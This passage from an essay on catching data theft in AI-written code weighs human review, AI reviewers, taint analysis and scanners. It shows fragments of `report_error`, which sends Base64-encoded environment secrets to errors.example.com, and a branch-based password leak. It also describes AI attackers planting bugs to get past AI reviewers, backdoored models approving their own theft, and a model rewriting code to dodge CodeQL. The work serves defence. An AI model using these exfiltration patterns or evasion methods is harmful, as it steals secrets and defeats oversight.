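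Accidental leaks are also the easiest to notice. A password in a public repository sits in plain text under a predictable file name, so anyone can search for it. Apiiro checked more than 100,000 files this way in three days. Nobody could search GitHub for victims of Meged's last attack, because its only trace was a slightly higher download count.

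## How much can people catch by reading the code?

Someone who reads `report_error` closely and knows what it is for has a good chance of catching the theft. But AI models now write more code than people can read closely. In experiments, most people who weren't looking for a security flaw missed the one in the code they were reading.

### More code than people can read

Claude wrote more than 90% of the contributions to Anthropic's code in September 2026, according to the company's stock-market filing. Business Standard's *Anthropic's internal Claude usage value exceeds monthly employee costs* reports that the daily volume of code per engineer in the third quarter was over 45 times the 2024 average.

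Both figures are hard to interpret. Infobae's *Claude escribió más del 90% del código de Anthropic en septiembre* (2026) says the filing doesn't define a contribution, or state how much of the generated code went into use without a person editing it. The Decoder's *Anthropic says Claude now writes over 90% of its code* gives only an eightfold increase for the second quarter, so the two figures may count different things. Other companies report lower shares. Thubron, in *Anthropic says more than 90% of its code is now written*, lists 75% for Google, 60% for Airbnb and 20% to 30% for Microsoft, but warns that some companies count all new code while others count only shipped code.

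A 2006 study published by SmartBear, which sells code-review software, found that reviewers at the network company Cisco caught the most defects when they read fewer than about 300 lines an hour. If an engineer wrote 100 lines a day in 2024, a colleague could read them at that rate in 20 minutes. Reading eight times as much code would take 2 hours and 40 minutes a day, and reading 45 times as much would take 15 hours.

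A new program of 20,000 lines would take 67 hours to read, or more than eight working days. Someone who reads twice as fast would still need about four days. Only one minute of the 67 hours would go to the five lines of `report_error`, but the reviewer doesn't know in advance where those lines are.

When a developer asks an agent to fix one thing, it may also change others, so the developer has to review the code again. One person may also be responsible for several agents. Ghaffary, in *Anthropic says Claude drives over 25% of its research and development*, reports that more than 30,000 agents were at work inside Anthropic at any one time in August 2026. The company had 5,300 employees at the end of September, which works out to nearly six agents per employee. Teams now use AI to review some of the code, but *CyberDual* (2026) found that AI reviewers have blind spots of their own.

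### How developers review in practice

Most developers know they should check AI-written code, but many don't always do it. Sonar, another seller of code-checking tools, published a survey of more than 1,100 developers in January 2026. In it, 96% did not fully trust AI-written code to work correctly, but only 48% said they always checked it before committing it.

Heavy users have similar worries. *Hedwig* (Shukla, Feng and Wang, 2026) surveyed 21 engineers, nearly all with at least eight years of programming experience. Thirteen worried about subtle bugs that get through review, and ten about security flaws. Yet 11 wanted the agent to consult them only at key milestones, and two wanted to be consulted only when something risky or unexpected happened.

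To find out what people do when they can't read everything, Dhanorkar, Passi and Vorvoreanu (2026), in *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice*, interviewed 17 experienced developers, 12 of them at Microsoft. The developers rarely watched an agent while it worked. Most of their checking came afterwards, and they relied on four shortcuts:

- They read the agent's plan and assumed that the agent had followed it.
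- They treated code that passed its tests as correct.
- They skimmed the code or the agent's summary for anything odd.
- They trusted the agent when they didn't know the subject themselves.

These are reasonable ways to find ordinary mistakes, but they would probably all miss `report_error`. A developer reading the plan would see that the agent was adding a crash reporter, which is true. The function would pass its tests, because it does send the error message to the monitoring service. Someone skimming the code would expect to find a `trace_id` in a crash report. A developer who has never used Base64 might assume that the monitoring service requires it.

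Some developers are stricter. In Dhanorkar and colleagues' study, one developer reported reading and approving every line when the code belongs to a larger system. Another had reviewed every line of a feature in Go, a language they hadn't known a month earlier, and thought the lines "looked legit". Reading every line gives little protection if the reader doesn't understand the code.

People look longer at code when it is labelled as AI-written. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues, 2026) tracked the eye movements of 32 software practitioners as they reviewed four Python files of about 77 lines each. Some passages were labelled as AI-written, although people had written all of them. The participants spent up to 60% longer looking at labelled passages when the code was complex, but their eye movements suggested that they read no more thoroughly. The study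 did not measure how many faults they found.

*Trust but Verify?* (Sakib, Banik and Jadliwala) examined 4,022 pull requests, which are proposed changes that people can review before adding them to a project, made by coding agents in real projects. Two language models checked 16,112 changes to risky files, such as build settings and shell scripts, for signs of poor security. They flagged 38.9% of the pull requests, and 53.6% of those with over 1,000 lines. Longer changes have more lines to flag, so the higher rate doesn't prove that people review them less carefully. Most of the flags (82.3%) concerned supply-chain weaknesses, typically packages or tools without a fixed version.

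The same pull requests contained 74 genuine secrets in plain text. Only 14 drew a warning during review, all from automated tools according to Sakib and colleagues, who conclude that reviewers missed the other 60, or 81.1%. However, one of their charts labels those 60 "silently removed", so somebody may have noticed a few and deleted them without comment. Still, a password in plain text is one of the easiest security problems to recognise. People had added about two thirds of the secrets, so distrusting the agent would not have been enough to prevent the leaks.

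### Experiments with planted flaws

Experiments can measure the catch rate, the share of defects that a check finds, because the researchers know which defects they planted. In an early example, *Poisoned ChatGPT Finds Work for Idle Hands* (2023), Oh, Lee and colleagues recruited 30 professional developers with an average of ten years' experience. They gave ten developers an AI tool that wrote whole passages of code on request, ten a tool that only completed lines, and ten no AI tool. The researchers had poisoned the model behind both tools so that it suggested insecure code, and they didn't tell the participants.

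Everyone had to encrypt social security numbers, search a database and look up an internet address. The table shows how many solutions contained each flaw, with the share that came directly from a poisoned suggestion in brackets:

| Flaw | Tool that writes passages | Tool that completes lines | No AI tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed encryption key | 100% (90%) | 80% (40%) | 44% |
| Weak encryption method | 80% (80%) | 30% (30%) | 11% |
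| Database query an attacker can alter | 90% (90%) | 80% (30%) | 90% |
| System command an attacker can alter | 70% (70%) | 50% (30%) | 20% |

Developers who received whole passages of code usually skimmed them, checked that they worked and submitted them. The 12 security specialists in the study did no better overall than the others, and one of them said there was no time for secure coding. People also write insecure code without help. In the database task, nine out of ten developers in the group with no AI tool made the same mistake.

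The model in that study is long out of date, but people's habits have changed less. In *Beware EviLLM*, Ryu, Chung and colleagues (2026) tested 21 people, mostly graduate students with security training, between November 2024 and May 2025. The participants used ChatGPT for two short programming tasks without knowing that the researchers had tampered with the setup. For eight of them, the researchers used hidden account settings to instruct ChatGPT to write insecure code. For the other 13, a browser extension replaced the code when they copied it.

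Seven of the eight participants in the first group and ten of the 13 in the second submitted code with both planted flaws. Only two participants reported anything odd, and one of these submitted clean code but thought a previous participant had left the strange text on the clipboard. Reading the code carefully on ChatGPT's page would not have helped the second group, because the flaw appeared only after pasting. A reviewer should therefore read the code in the project itself, as it will run.

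Participants who said they had considered that the code might be malicious missed fewer flaws, while programming skill and confidence made no clear difference. With 21 people and several factors to compare, the link with suspicion could be chance. But a larger experiment points the same way. In *Less is More* (2022), 150 developers reviewed code that contained two security flaws:

| Reviewers | Found the harder flaw | Found the easier flaw |
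|---|---|---|
| 33 with no special instructions | 3% | 21% |
| 117 told to look for security problems | 46% | 62% |

So a sentence of instruction helped far more than years of experience had in the other studies. *The AI tool can't make it any worse* (Yardim, Serafini and colleagues, 2026) also found that explicit security instructions could steer developers who used AI assistants towards secure results.

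Some developers accept insecure advice from an AI assistant even after a warning. In *Exploring the Impact of Intervention Methods on Developers’ Security Behavior*, Naiakshina, Yardim and Serafini (2025) gave freelance developers a manipulated assistant that recommended an outdated way to store passwords. Of those notified that the advice was insecure, 32% still accepted it, often with confidence. According to *Helpful or Harmful?* (2026), an earlier experiment by Perry and colleagues found that developers with an AI model wrote less secure code on four of five tasks but rated their solutions as more secure.

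All these experiments used planted security flaws, and data theft could be easier or harder to spot. A reader needs specialist knowledge to recognise a weak encryption method, but can question `report_error` just by knowing what a crash report is for. However, a thief can put more effort into the disguise. The participants also had only a short piece of code to read, and in *Less is More* all of them had a flaw to find. A working reviewer may read thousands of harmless changes before a malicious one arrives, and it is hard to stay suspicious for that long.

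### The xz backdoor

In February 2024, a new release of XZ Utils, a set of compression tools found on most Linux systems, contained a backdoor. The person responsible used the name Jia Tan and had been sending the project useful improvements since 2021. Other accounts, which may have belonged to the same attacker, complained that the volunteer maintainer, Lasse Collin, was working too slowly. Collin gradually gave Jia Tan more responsibility, including the right to publish releases.

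Most of the attack was outside the source code that a reviewer would normally read. Jia Tan hid compiled malicious code in two compressed files that looked like test samples, one of them supposedly damaged on purpose. During the build, a script unpacked the code and added it to the finished library. Jia Tan left the lines that started this process out of the public repository, where other developers could follow each change, and put them only in the release archive that Linux distributors download and build.

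On some systems, the program that handles remote logins loads this library. The backdoor let anyone with the attacker's private key run commands on those systems without a valid login, so an attacker could have read any secret stored there.

Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer, found the backdoor by accident. Logins to a test machine were using too much processor time and took about 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. Freund traced the delay to the library and published the finding on 29 March 2024. By then the release had mainly reached test versions of Linux, so the attack probably did little damage. Within months, the backdoor could have been on many servers.

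Someone could have read every line of the program's source in the repository without finding the attack. Comparing the release archive with the repository would have revealed the extra lines, but they might not have looked alarming, because release archives often contain build files that the repository lacks. A developer can guard against this kind of attack by building the software from the reviewed repository on a clean machine and refusing any binary file whose purpose nobody can explain.

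The same precautions make sense for a coding agent, which may edit build scripts and test files along with the program. If an agent put the data-stealing code in a build script, `report_error` could look clean in the source. The xz attack also shows that a long record of useful contributions doesn't prove that a contributor, human or model, is honest.

### Reading the lines that matter

Human review still has an advantage because a person often knows what the code is supposed to do, and no one can tell from the code alone whether `report_error` is stealing data. *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (2022) cites OWASP's view that secure code review is probably the single most effective technique for finding security bugs early.

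Two of the cases described earlier support this view, because the malicious part was visible to anyone who looked. A GitHub user spotted the malware that Mythos 5 had hidden in a code change, and a careful reader could have stopped the script that emptied the Solana trader's wallet.

The practical problem is getting a wary reviewer to look at the right lines. Keeping changes small helps. A reviewer who reads 300 lines an hour can finish a 300-line change in one sitting, and anything unrelated to the change's purpose stands out more. Several of the developers whom Dhanorkar and colleagues interviewed divided their work into small tasks for this reason. But if an agent produces 4,500 lines a day, reviewing them at that rate takes 15 hours, even when they are split into 15 changes.

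Teams therefore also need a rule about which changes a person must always read. To catch theft, it should cover changes that touch secrets, network calls, build scripts or dependencies (the outside packages a program relies on). If these make up 5% of a 20,000-line program, reading those 1,000 lines takes 3 hours and 20 minutes, compared with 67 hours for the whole program. The share will vary between programs. Such a rule also suits developers' preferences, since Shukla and colleagues found that the same programmer may want strict control over some files and much less over others.

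GitHub can enforce part of the rule by requiring a named person's approval before anyone changes certain files. This works well for build scripts and package lists, which have predictable names, but network calls can appear in any file, so a team also needs an automatic search for terms such as `os.environ` and `http.client`. The agent shouldn't decide which of its own changes are sensitive, because it could leave out a sensitive one, deliberately or by mistake.

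The reviewer also needs something to compare the code with. For network calls, this can be a written list of the outside addresses that the program should contact and the data that each should receive:

| Address | Purpose | Data it may receive |
|---|---|---|
| errors.example.com | Crash reports | Error message and a random identifier |
| payments.example.com | Card payments | Order number, amount and payment token |

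The last column is essential. The developer asked for crash reports to go to a monitoring service, so errors.example.com may well be on the list, and a reviewer who checked only the address would approve `report_error`. A reviewer using the full list also has to check where `trace_id` comes from. Two lines up, the code shows that it comes from `os.environ`, so it isn't a random identifier. A person should write the list before the agent starts, because an agent that planned to steal data could otherwise describe the data in a way that made sending it look acceptable.

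The original prompt is also worth keeping with the code. In the eye-tracking study, 14 of the 32 participants used the prompt to guide their review, and some of them treated it as a requirement to check the code against. Reviewers should get specific instructions too, such as "Find every place where this code reads a secret, and check where the value goes" rather than "review this change".

For the most sensitive code, a team can ask two people to read it separately. In *Less is More*, instructed reviewers had a 46% chance of catching the harder flaw. If two such reviewers make independent mistakes, the chance that at least one catches it is 1 − 0.54², or about 71%. The real figure is probably lower, because people with similar training tend to overlook the same things.

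An attacker can also make the important lines harder to recognise. Suppose a new change copies the environment into a harmless-sounding variable called `context`, which a file the team approved months ago already sends to the monitoring service. The change contains no network call, so a reviewer would have to follow `context` from one file to the other, perhaps through a dozen functions, and people are bad at doing that for hours.

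## How much do AI reviewers catch?

An AI reviewer can follow a variable like `context` through a dozen functions without tiring, so it can read all the code that a team's agents write. In October 2026, *CyberDual* tested three AI reviewers on 1,088 planted bugs. The reviewers caught between 85% and 91% of the bugs, but they often missed the same ones. A reviewer with a high catch rate can also raise so many false alarms that the team misses a real theft.

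### How an AI reviewer works

The simplest AI reviewer is a model that receives the changed lines and returns a verdict. It would have trouble with `context`, because the line that sends the variable is in a file the change doesn't touch. Newer reviewers are agents that also search the rest of the repository for related code, and may run the program or write tests for it. Then they approve the change, comment on it or repair it. *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2025) found that GPT-5 caught more critical problems and raised fewer false alarms when it could search the repository and run code.

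Anthropic's reviewer runs several agents at once, each looking for a different kind of problem. A further step checks their findings against what the code does, according to Anthropic's *Set up Code Review for Claude Code*. *Bringing Code Review to Claude Code* reports that reviews average 20 minutes and $15 to $25, and that a person gives final approval. Anthropic's engineers marked fewer than 1% of the findings as incorrect, but that figure doesn't measure how many problems the agents missed.

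OpenAI deliberately let its reviewer miss some problems so that developers would trust the comments it did make. Trębacz and colleagues argue that people stop using a tool that raises too many false alarms. Accepting some misses is sensible for ordinary bugs, which a team can often fix later, but nobody can take back a stolen password. A team worried about theft may therefore want the reviewer to flag more possible problems, at least in code that handles secrets. OpenAI's reviewer accepts instructions to do this.

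### Bugs planted in real projects

CyberDual had six AI models attack 14 widely used C and C++ libraries, including XZ Utils. Each model had to plant a bug and write an exploit, a small program that used the bug to crash the library. The reviewers were Claude Code running Sonnet 5, Claude Code running Opus 4.8, and Codex running GPT-6-Sol. They saw the code change but not the exploit, and had to approve or repair the change. The researchers then ran the exploit on the reviewed code. They counted the attack as surviving if the exploit still worked, regardless of what the reviewer had reported.

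The result depended heavily on the attacker's task:

| Attacker's task | Attacks | Survived Sonnet 5 | Survived Opus 4.8 | Survived GPT-6-Sol | Survived all three |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| One assigned change | 349 | 2.3% | 1.1% | 0% | 0 |
| One change, with the project's real fix to imitate | 312 | 13.9% | 13.3% | 5.4% | 11 |
| A bug split between two or more changes in a history of 50 to 199 real ones | 427 | 24.4% | 17.1% | 19.4% | 17 |
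| All | 1,088 | 14.3% | 10.9% | 9.2% | 28 |

The amount of code explains part of the difference. Sonnet 5 reviewed 143 of the spread-out attacks twice. It caught 80% when given the full history and 90% when given only the altered changes and those that depended on them, though the final code was identical. In a smaller test on the JavaScript engines of Chrome and Firefox, which are much larger programs, Sonnet 5 caught 22 of 32 spread-out attacks and GPT-6-Sol caught 16. So the advice to keep changes small applies to AI reviewers too.

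Some reviewers missed a bug because they never looked at it. In more than a third of their misses on the spread-out attacks, Sonnet 5 and GPT-6-Sol had not displayed any of the planted lines. A team could therefore require a record showing that the reviewer displayed every changed line. Reviewers that wrote their own test inputs caught more, perhaps partly because they wrote tests when they already suspected something. Running the project's existing tests did not help.

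In 79 of the 100 attacks GPT-6-Sol missed, it rejected the change but repaired the wrong code. A team that discarded every rejected change instead of merging the repair would have stopped those 79, and only 21 attacks (about 2%) would have got through. The same policy would have cut Sonnet 5's misses only from 154 to 125. The policy works only if nobody overrules the rejection. In about nine out of ten of these wrong repairs, GPT-6-Sol's report didn't name the planted code, so a developer who looked into the complaint might well have dismissed it.

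### Would theft be easier to spot?

All the bugs in this experiment were memory-safety bugs, in which a program reads or writes outside the memory set aside for it. None of them stole data, so the catch rates may not apply to code that does.

Data theft could be easier to catch than a memory-safety bug because the code must contain both a source of data and a channel for sending it out. A memory-safety bug may be just a missing check, which can pass for an honest mistake.

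On the other hand, the reviewers had two advantages they would not have when looking for data theft. Their instructions named the kind of bug to look for, and they could confirm a suspicion by running the program with a tool that reports memory errors. No similar tool can identify theft from the fact that a program sent a password, because legitimate programs send passwords whenever they log in. Crude theft is probably still easier to catch than these bugs, but theft that sends data to an approved address might be harder.

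Research on malicious packages gives more direct evidence. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, tested 11 tools on 6,420 malicious npm packages and 7,288 popular harmless ones. About two thirds of the malicious packages sent data to an attacker. The best tool, IntelGuard, which uses a language model, caught 93.8% of the malicious packages, including 98.5% of those that sent data out, and wrongly flagged 108 harmless ones (1.5%).

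SocketAI, another tool using the same small model, GPT-4.1 mini, caught only 44%. It asked the model to judge the code without other information and then to challenge its own findings, and this second step made the model reverse many correct answers. SocketAI also read no more than 20 files per package. IntelGuard instead gave the model similar examples of known malware and asked whether the code fitted the package's stated purpose. A developer can similarly give an AI reviewer the original request and a list of permitted addresses and data.

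Other tools have done even better. *CHASE* (Toda and Mori, 2026) describes a team of AI agents that caught 98.4% of 500 malicious Python packages and flagged only two of 2,500 harmless ones. The monitoring company Datadog runs an AI reviewer on its own code and on outside packages. *From single pull requests to full software packages* (Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues) reports that this reviewer detected 95.5% of known malicious packages.

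Datadog's reviewer also recognises credential theft in individual changes. *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*, by Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues, shows its verdict on a change from a real attack on the Nx project. The change sent the token for publishing packages to an outside address, and the reviewer identified both the theft and the destination. In early 2026 the reviewer helped Datadog discover malicious pull requests that an AI agent had sent to two of the company's public repositories, according to Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper.

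But most malicious packages are easy to catch. Guo and colleagues found that 80.3% used no evasion techniques, whereas CyberDual's attackers knew they had to get past a reviewer. Credential theft was also among the behaviours the tools as a group were worst at detecting, because it uses the same functions as legitimate login code. Some attacks are in code that a tool doesn't read. *MalTotal* (2026) missed malicious code in a package's dependencies, and *CASHEWS* (2026) describes a June 2026 attack whose malicious file was 4.5 megabytes, too long for many models to read in one go.

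### Why reviewers miss the same attacks

All three reviewers missed the same 28 of the 1,088 attacks, about 18 times as many as expected if their misses were independent. In that case, multiplying their individual miss rates (0.143 × 0.109 × 0.092) gives about 0.14%, or 1.6 attacks.

Some of that gap comes from mixing easy and hard tasks. Calculating the expected number separately for each row of the table raises it to 3.8. That is still far below 28, so the attacks within each row must also have varied in difficulty.

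A few hard cases can produce such a gap, even if the reviewers have nothing in common. Suppose that 100 of 1,000 attacks are hard, and that each of three reviewers independently misses 65% of the hard ones and 4% of the rest, or about 10% overall. We would then expect about 27 attacks (100 × 0.65³) to get past all three reviewers, nearly all of them hard. If all the attacks were equally hard and each reviewer still missed 10%, we would expect only one to get past all three. An attack might be hard for every reviewer because the important line is one among thousands, or because the code looks complete to anyone who doesn't know what is missing.

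Similar training probably makes the overlap worse. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that models tend to make the same mistakes, especially if they are accurate or come from the same developer. Shared mistakes also weaken majority votes. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), when models got a legal question wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 87% of the time on average. A majority vote of 15 models was right on 84.3% of questions, compared with 90.5% for the best single model. On 98.4% of questions, at least one model was right.

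A team with several AI reviewers should therefore investigate whenever any of them objects, instead of counting votes. In CyberDual, only 28 attacks (2.6%) got past every reviewer, so a team that acted correctly on each catch would have stopped all the others. This approach also produces more false alarms. Three reviewers that each wrongly flag 2% of harmless changes could together flag almost 6%.

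### A reviewer from a second vendor

GPT-6-Sol caught 69% of the attacks that Sonnet 5 missed. This is well below the 91% it caught overall, because the attacks Sonnet 5 missed were harder than average. Using both reviewers would still have cut the share of missed attacks from 14.3% with Sonnet 5 alone to about 4.4%.

In one of the three setups, where attackers had a real fix to imitate, adding a second model from the same vendor helped much less than adding one from another vendor. Sonnet 5 missed 42 attacks in that setup, and Opus 4.8 caught only about 12 of those, judging by the published measure of agreement between the two Claude models. GPT-6-Sol caught at least 25 of the 42, since it missed only 17 attacks in the whole setup. When attacks were spread over a project's history, the two Claude models had far fewer misses in common, so a second Claude model was useful there too.

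A second vendor's model can also break working code if it is allowed to rewrite it. Xiang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Cross-Model LLM Code Review*, had Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 review each other's solutions to 116 programming-contest problems without running them. Claude's review raised the share of GPT-5.5's programs that worked from 71.6% to 89.7%. But GPT-5.5's review lowered Claude's share from 91.4% to 82.8%, fixing three programs and breaking 13. The experiment tested for ordinary mistakes, not attacks. It suggests that a second reviewer should point out problems and leave the repair to the model that wrote the code or to a person, particularly if the reviewer is the weaker programmer.

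### When the author reviews its own work

Many developers ask an agent to check the code it has just written. *Self-Attribution Bias* (Khullar, Hopkins et al., 2026) found that this makes models too lenient. Ten models rated the same code as safer and more correct when asked to review it in the conversation where they had written it. In one test, reviewing in the same conversation made a model five times as likely to approve a change in which it had followed a malicious instruction hidden in the project.

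A model's leniency towards its own code comes more from reviewing it in the same conversation than from knowing that it wrote it. When Khullar and colleagues showed a model the code in a new conversation and told it that it had written the code, its ratings barely changed. *Style, Not Self* (2026) found that models mostly can't recognise their own code. An easy fix is to start the review in a new session that contains the code and its purpose but not the reasoning of the model that wrote it. *Cross-Context Review* (2026) found that a review in a new session worked better than a second review in the original one.

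The CyberDual reviewers all started in a new session, and they were only slightly worse at catching attacks by their own model. When attacks were spread over project history, Sonnet 5 missed 28% of its own and 24% of all such attacks. The figures were 19% and 17% for Opus 4.8, and 23% and 19% for GPT-6-Sol. Each model had planted only 54 to 70 of these attacks, so the differences could be due to chance.

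A fresh session does not help if the model itself is malicious, because the new copy has the same weights. For example, if a backdoored model starts writing code that steals data on a certain date, the same date might trigger the reviewing copy to approve that code. A model from another vendor is unlikely to have the same backdoor, but it gives less protection against a scam address that both models learned from the web or an injected instruction that both read.

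### 223 alarms for one attack

When malicious changes are rare, a reviewer with a high catch rate can still raise mostly false alarms. Suppose one change in 10,000 is malicious, and a reviewer catches 90% of malicious changes and wrongly flags 2% of harmless ones. Out of a million changes, 100 are malicious, and the reviewer catches 90 of them. It also flags 2% of the 999,900 harmless changes, which is 19,998 false alarms. Only 90 of its 20,088 alarms, or about one in 223, are real.

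At Datadog, which handles nearly 10,000 pull requests a week, these rates would mean about 200 false alarms and one real attack a week. If each alarm took ten minutes to check, the false ones would take 33 hours. People would probably start dismissing alarms after a few weeks, and might then dismiss the real one.

The 2% is an assumption, because the CyberDual researchers did not measure how often their reviewers rejected harmless changes. IntelGuard's 1.5% suggests that it is realistic. The table applies the same calculation to the package detectors, first with one malicious item in 10,000 and then with one in 38:

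| Reviewer | Catch rate | False-alarm rate | Alarms per attack caught, 1 in 10,000 malicious | Alarms per attack caught, 1 in 38 malicious |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Example above | 90% | 2% | 223 | 1.8 |
| IntelGuard | 93.8% | 1.5% | 159 | 1.6 |
| CHASE | 98.4% | 0.08% | 9 | 1.03 |

The last column is close to what *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026) found among new packages on PyPI. Its detector scanned 8,249 packages over three months and flagged 233, and PyPI's maintainers confirmed and removed 219 of them. Malware is so common there that even a mediocre detector's alarms are right about half the time. A company's own code should contain far fewer attacks. If only one change in a million were malicious, even a detector with CHASE's rates would raise about 800 alarms for each attack it caught.

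Many false alarms happen because harmless code can look suspicious. *CASHEWS* describes a harmless package that a model flagged just because it contained Base64-encoded code. A reviewer that reacts to Base64 would flag `report_error`, but also a lot of harmless code. Other false alarms are simple mistakes. *PyFEX* (2026) flagged ten harmless packages, and for eight of them the model analysed the code correctly but then gave the wrong verdict.

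Datadog cut its AI reviewer's false-alarm rate from over 10% to 0.03%, which would mean about three false alarms a week. Lamb and colleagues credit better instructions, a growing set of labelled examples and rules that exclude patterns known to be safe. They tested the reviewer on only a few hundred pull requests, too few to establish such a low rate, so the figure is presumably also based on the months of live use.

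The company later split the review into two stages. A cheap model screens every change, and a stronger one investigates the suspicious ones, for instance by checking the contributor's history. On 690 test changes, this reduced the false alarms from 17 to none, though by the 3/n rule a true false-alarm rate of 0.4% would still fit that result. An attack that the first stage clears never reaches the second, so Doutre and colleagues made the first stage flag changes more readily. They also added an automatic check for lookalike web addresses, which the first stage had been missing.

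A team can also reduce the alarms by checking for theft only in the sensitive changes that a person must always read. If these make up 5% of all changes and include every malicious one, then one in 500 of them is malicious, and the reviewer in the first example raises about 12 alarms for each attack it catches instead of 223. However, the reviewer will miss any attack outside that 5%.

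## What can static analysis and mathematical proof establish?

Static analysis can follow a variable such as `context` across all the files in a program, and it gives the same result every time. A mathematical proof can cover every possible run of a program, including runs that no tester would think of. Either could in principle rule out a theft like the one in `report_error`. But most of today's tools and proofs deal with security flaws, and a program can send a password to a stranger without having any such flaw.

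### Following a password through the code

Taint analysis is static analysis that follows data from a sensitive source to a sink, a place where the data could leave the program. Most security tools use it instead to look for incoming attacks. *Making Small Code LLMs More Efficient for Secure Code Review* (2026) describes the usual setup, in which the source is untrusted data from outside and the sink is a dangerous operation inside the program. To look for theft, a developer has to relabel secrets as sources and network calls as sinks.

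In `report_error`, the source is `os.environ`, which holds the program's environment variables, and the sink is `request`, which sends data. The tool goes through the code and keeps a list of tainted values, meaning values that may contain something from the source:

| Code | What the tool concludes | Newly tainted |
|---|---|---|
| `os.environ` | This is a source | `os.environ` |
| `env = json.dumps(dict(os.environ))` | Turning the variables into text keeps their content | `env` |
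| `trace_id = base64.b64encode(env.encode()).decode()` | Base64 rewrites the text but keeps its content | `trace_id` |
| `report = json.dumps({"error": str(err), "trace_id": trace_id})` | The report contains `trace_id` | `report` |
| `.request("POST", "/", report)` | A tainted value has reached a sink | Alarm |

The tool then reports the whole path, from `os.environ` through `env`, `trace_id` and `report` to `request`. The name `trace_id` and the Base64 encoding might fool a person, but the tool ignores the name and treats the encoding as one more step that passes the data on.

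In a longer program, the tool repeats the process until a full pass adds nothing to the list. This must eventually happen because the program's text contains a finite number of variables. When one function passes a tainted value to another, the tool keeps tracking it in the second function. It could therefore follow `context` from a new change into the file the team approved months ago, if it analyses the whole repository and not just the changed lines.

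CodeQL, the tool behind GitHub's code scanning, works in roughly this way. *Preserve the Vulnerability, Break the Alert* (Cao, Ding and Xu, 2026) found that ordinary rewording of the code, such as adding intermediate variables, almost never made CodeQL lose track of the data. CodeQL is weaker where data passes into or out of the code it analyses.

### Where the trail ends

The first of these edges is the library. `json.dumps` and `b64encode` are library functions, and a taint analyser usually doesn't read their code. It relies on handwritten summaries of how each function passes data on. Cao and colleagues explain that the analyser treats a call without a summary as passing on no taint. If the tool had no summary for `b64encode`, it would treat `trace_id` as clean and raise no alarm. A tool could instead assume that every unknown function passes on any taint it receives, but it would then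 raise many more false alarms.

The trail can also end at a file or database. Suppose one program saves its environment in a cache file, and another uploads the cache every night. Neither program has both a labelled source and a sink. If a developer labelled every file as a source, the analysis would flag the nightly upload, but it would also flag a program that uploads holiday photos.

Static analysis tools read a program before it runs, so they can't analyse code that the program later assembles as text or downloads, and then executes. Banning this practice is easier than analysing it. In Python, a simple search finds `exec` and `eval`, the usual functions for running text as code, and most programs can do without them.

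The hardest case is a program that reveals a secret without copying it:

```python
if db_password < "n":
    path = "/a"
else:
    path = "/b"
http.client.HTTPSConnection("errors.example.com").request("GET", path)
```

`path` never contains any part of the password, so an analyser that tracks only copied values won't flag the code. But whoever runs the server learns whether the password comes before or after "n" in the computer's alphabetical order. A random 12-character password, with each character chosen from 64 possibilities, has 6 bits per character, or 72 in total, so 72 well-chosen yes-or-no questions would reveal all of it.

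A tool can deal with this by tainting everything that depends on which branch the program took. But every login page also branches on a password, so the tool would report even the message "wrong password" as a leak. Strictly speaking it is one, since a stranger learns from it that one guess was incorrect.

These gaps matter most when someone keeps editing code until the tool stops flagging it. Cao and colleagues asked Claude Opus 4.7 to rewrite code containing 172 real flaws that CodeQL had detected, so that each flaw remained but CodeQL no longer flagged it. The rewrites had to look like routine maintenance. With three attempts per flaw, the model succeeded for about a quarter of them, always by exploiting a gap in CodeQL's information about libraries. A second, independently built analyser also missed the flaws in many of the successful rewrites. When the researchers asked the model only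 to tidy the same functions, without mentioning CodeQL's warnings, CodeQL still flagged every flaw.

The same kind of gap could hide the theft of a password, although these flaws did not involve data theft. An agent told to "fix this alarm" might also make such a rewrite with no bad intent, because its only sign of success is that the alarm disappears.

### Was the data supposed to go there?

A taint analyser can find a path from a secret to the network, but it cannot tell whether the user wanted the data to take it. Most programs that hold a password send it somewhere. The web shop has to log in to its database, with a line such as this:

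```python
connect("db.example.com", password=os.environ["DB_PASSWORD"])
```

The tool can't easily distinguish this from `report_error`, since both take a value from the environment and send it over the network. If it flags both, developers will soon learn to dismiss its warnings.

The tool therefore needs a policy, and the written list of addresses and data that helps a human reviewer can serve as one. For the web shop, it might contain these rules:

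| Data | Where it may go |
|---|---|
| `DB_PASSWORD` | db.example.com |
| `PAYMENT_KEY` | payments.example.com |
| Everything else in the environment | Nowhere |

The database login now passes, but `report_error` still triggers an alarm because it sends the entire environment, including the database password, to errors.example.com. Checking the address's reputation would not resolve the alarm, because even a reputable monitoring service should not receive that password.

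This works best when the address is written out in the code. If the program reads the address from a settings file or builds it while running, the tool may not be able to tell where the data goes. A cautious team would treat that as a violation and have the agent write the address directly in the code.

### Secret scanners and flaw scanners

Developers may already run a secret scanner, which searches for passwords and keys written into code. It looks for known formats, such as the fixed prefix of a cloud provider's keys, and for long strings that look random. It is a good defence against accidental leaks, though the leaked Claude Code settings files showed that it misses some. But a clean result is no evidence against theft, because code like `report_error` contains no password and picks one up only when it runs.

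A rule-based flaw scanner compares code with patterns of known mistakes, such as a database query that an attacker can alter. AI-written code can contain many such mistakes. In *Cybersecurity Risks of AI-Generated Code* (2024), Ji, Jun and colleagues gave five models prompts designed to bring out insecure code, and almost half of the resulting snippets contained bugs. *Insecure by design?*, by Glas, Nirschl and colleagues, warns that AI-written code can contain a familiar flaw in an unfamiliar form, which a scanner built around human habits may miss.

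By the usual rules, though, `report_error` is acceptable code, because it uses an encrypted connection and passes no outside text to a database or a command line. A team could add its own rule against reading all the environment variables at once. This would catch the function, and few legitimate functions would break the rule, because most need only one or two variables. However, the rule would miss malicious code that read only `DB_PASSWORD`.

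### How often the tools are right

Published results for static analysis vary widely, and some are very poor. *Fixed Detectors, Moving Code* (2026) tested Semgrep, a popular scanner that matches patterns in source code, on nearly 20,000 C and C++ cases. Semgrep flagged 46.5% of the vulnerable cases and 47.9% of the fixed ones, so its alarms didn't help show whether a flaw was still there. One possible reason is that a fix often changes only a line or two and leaves the risky-looking code that triggered the rule.

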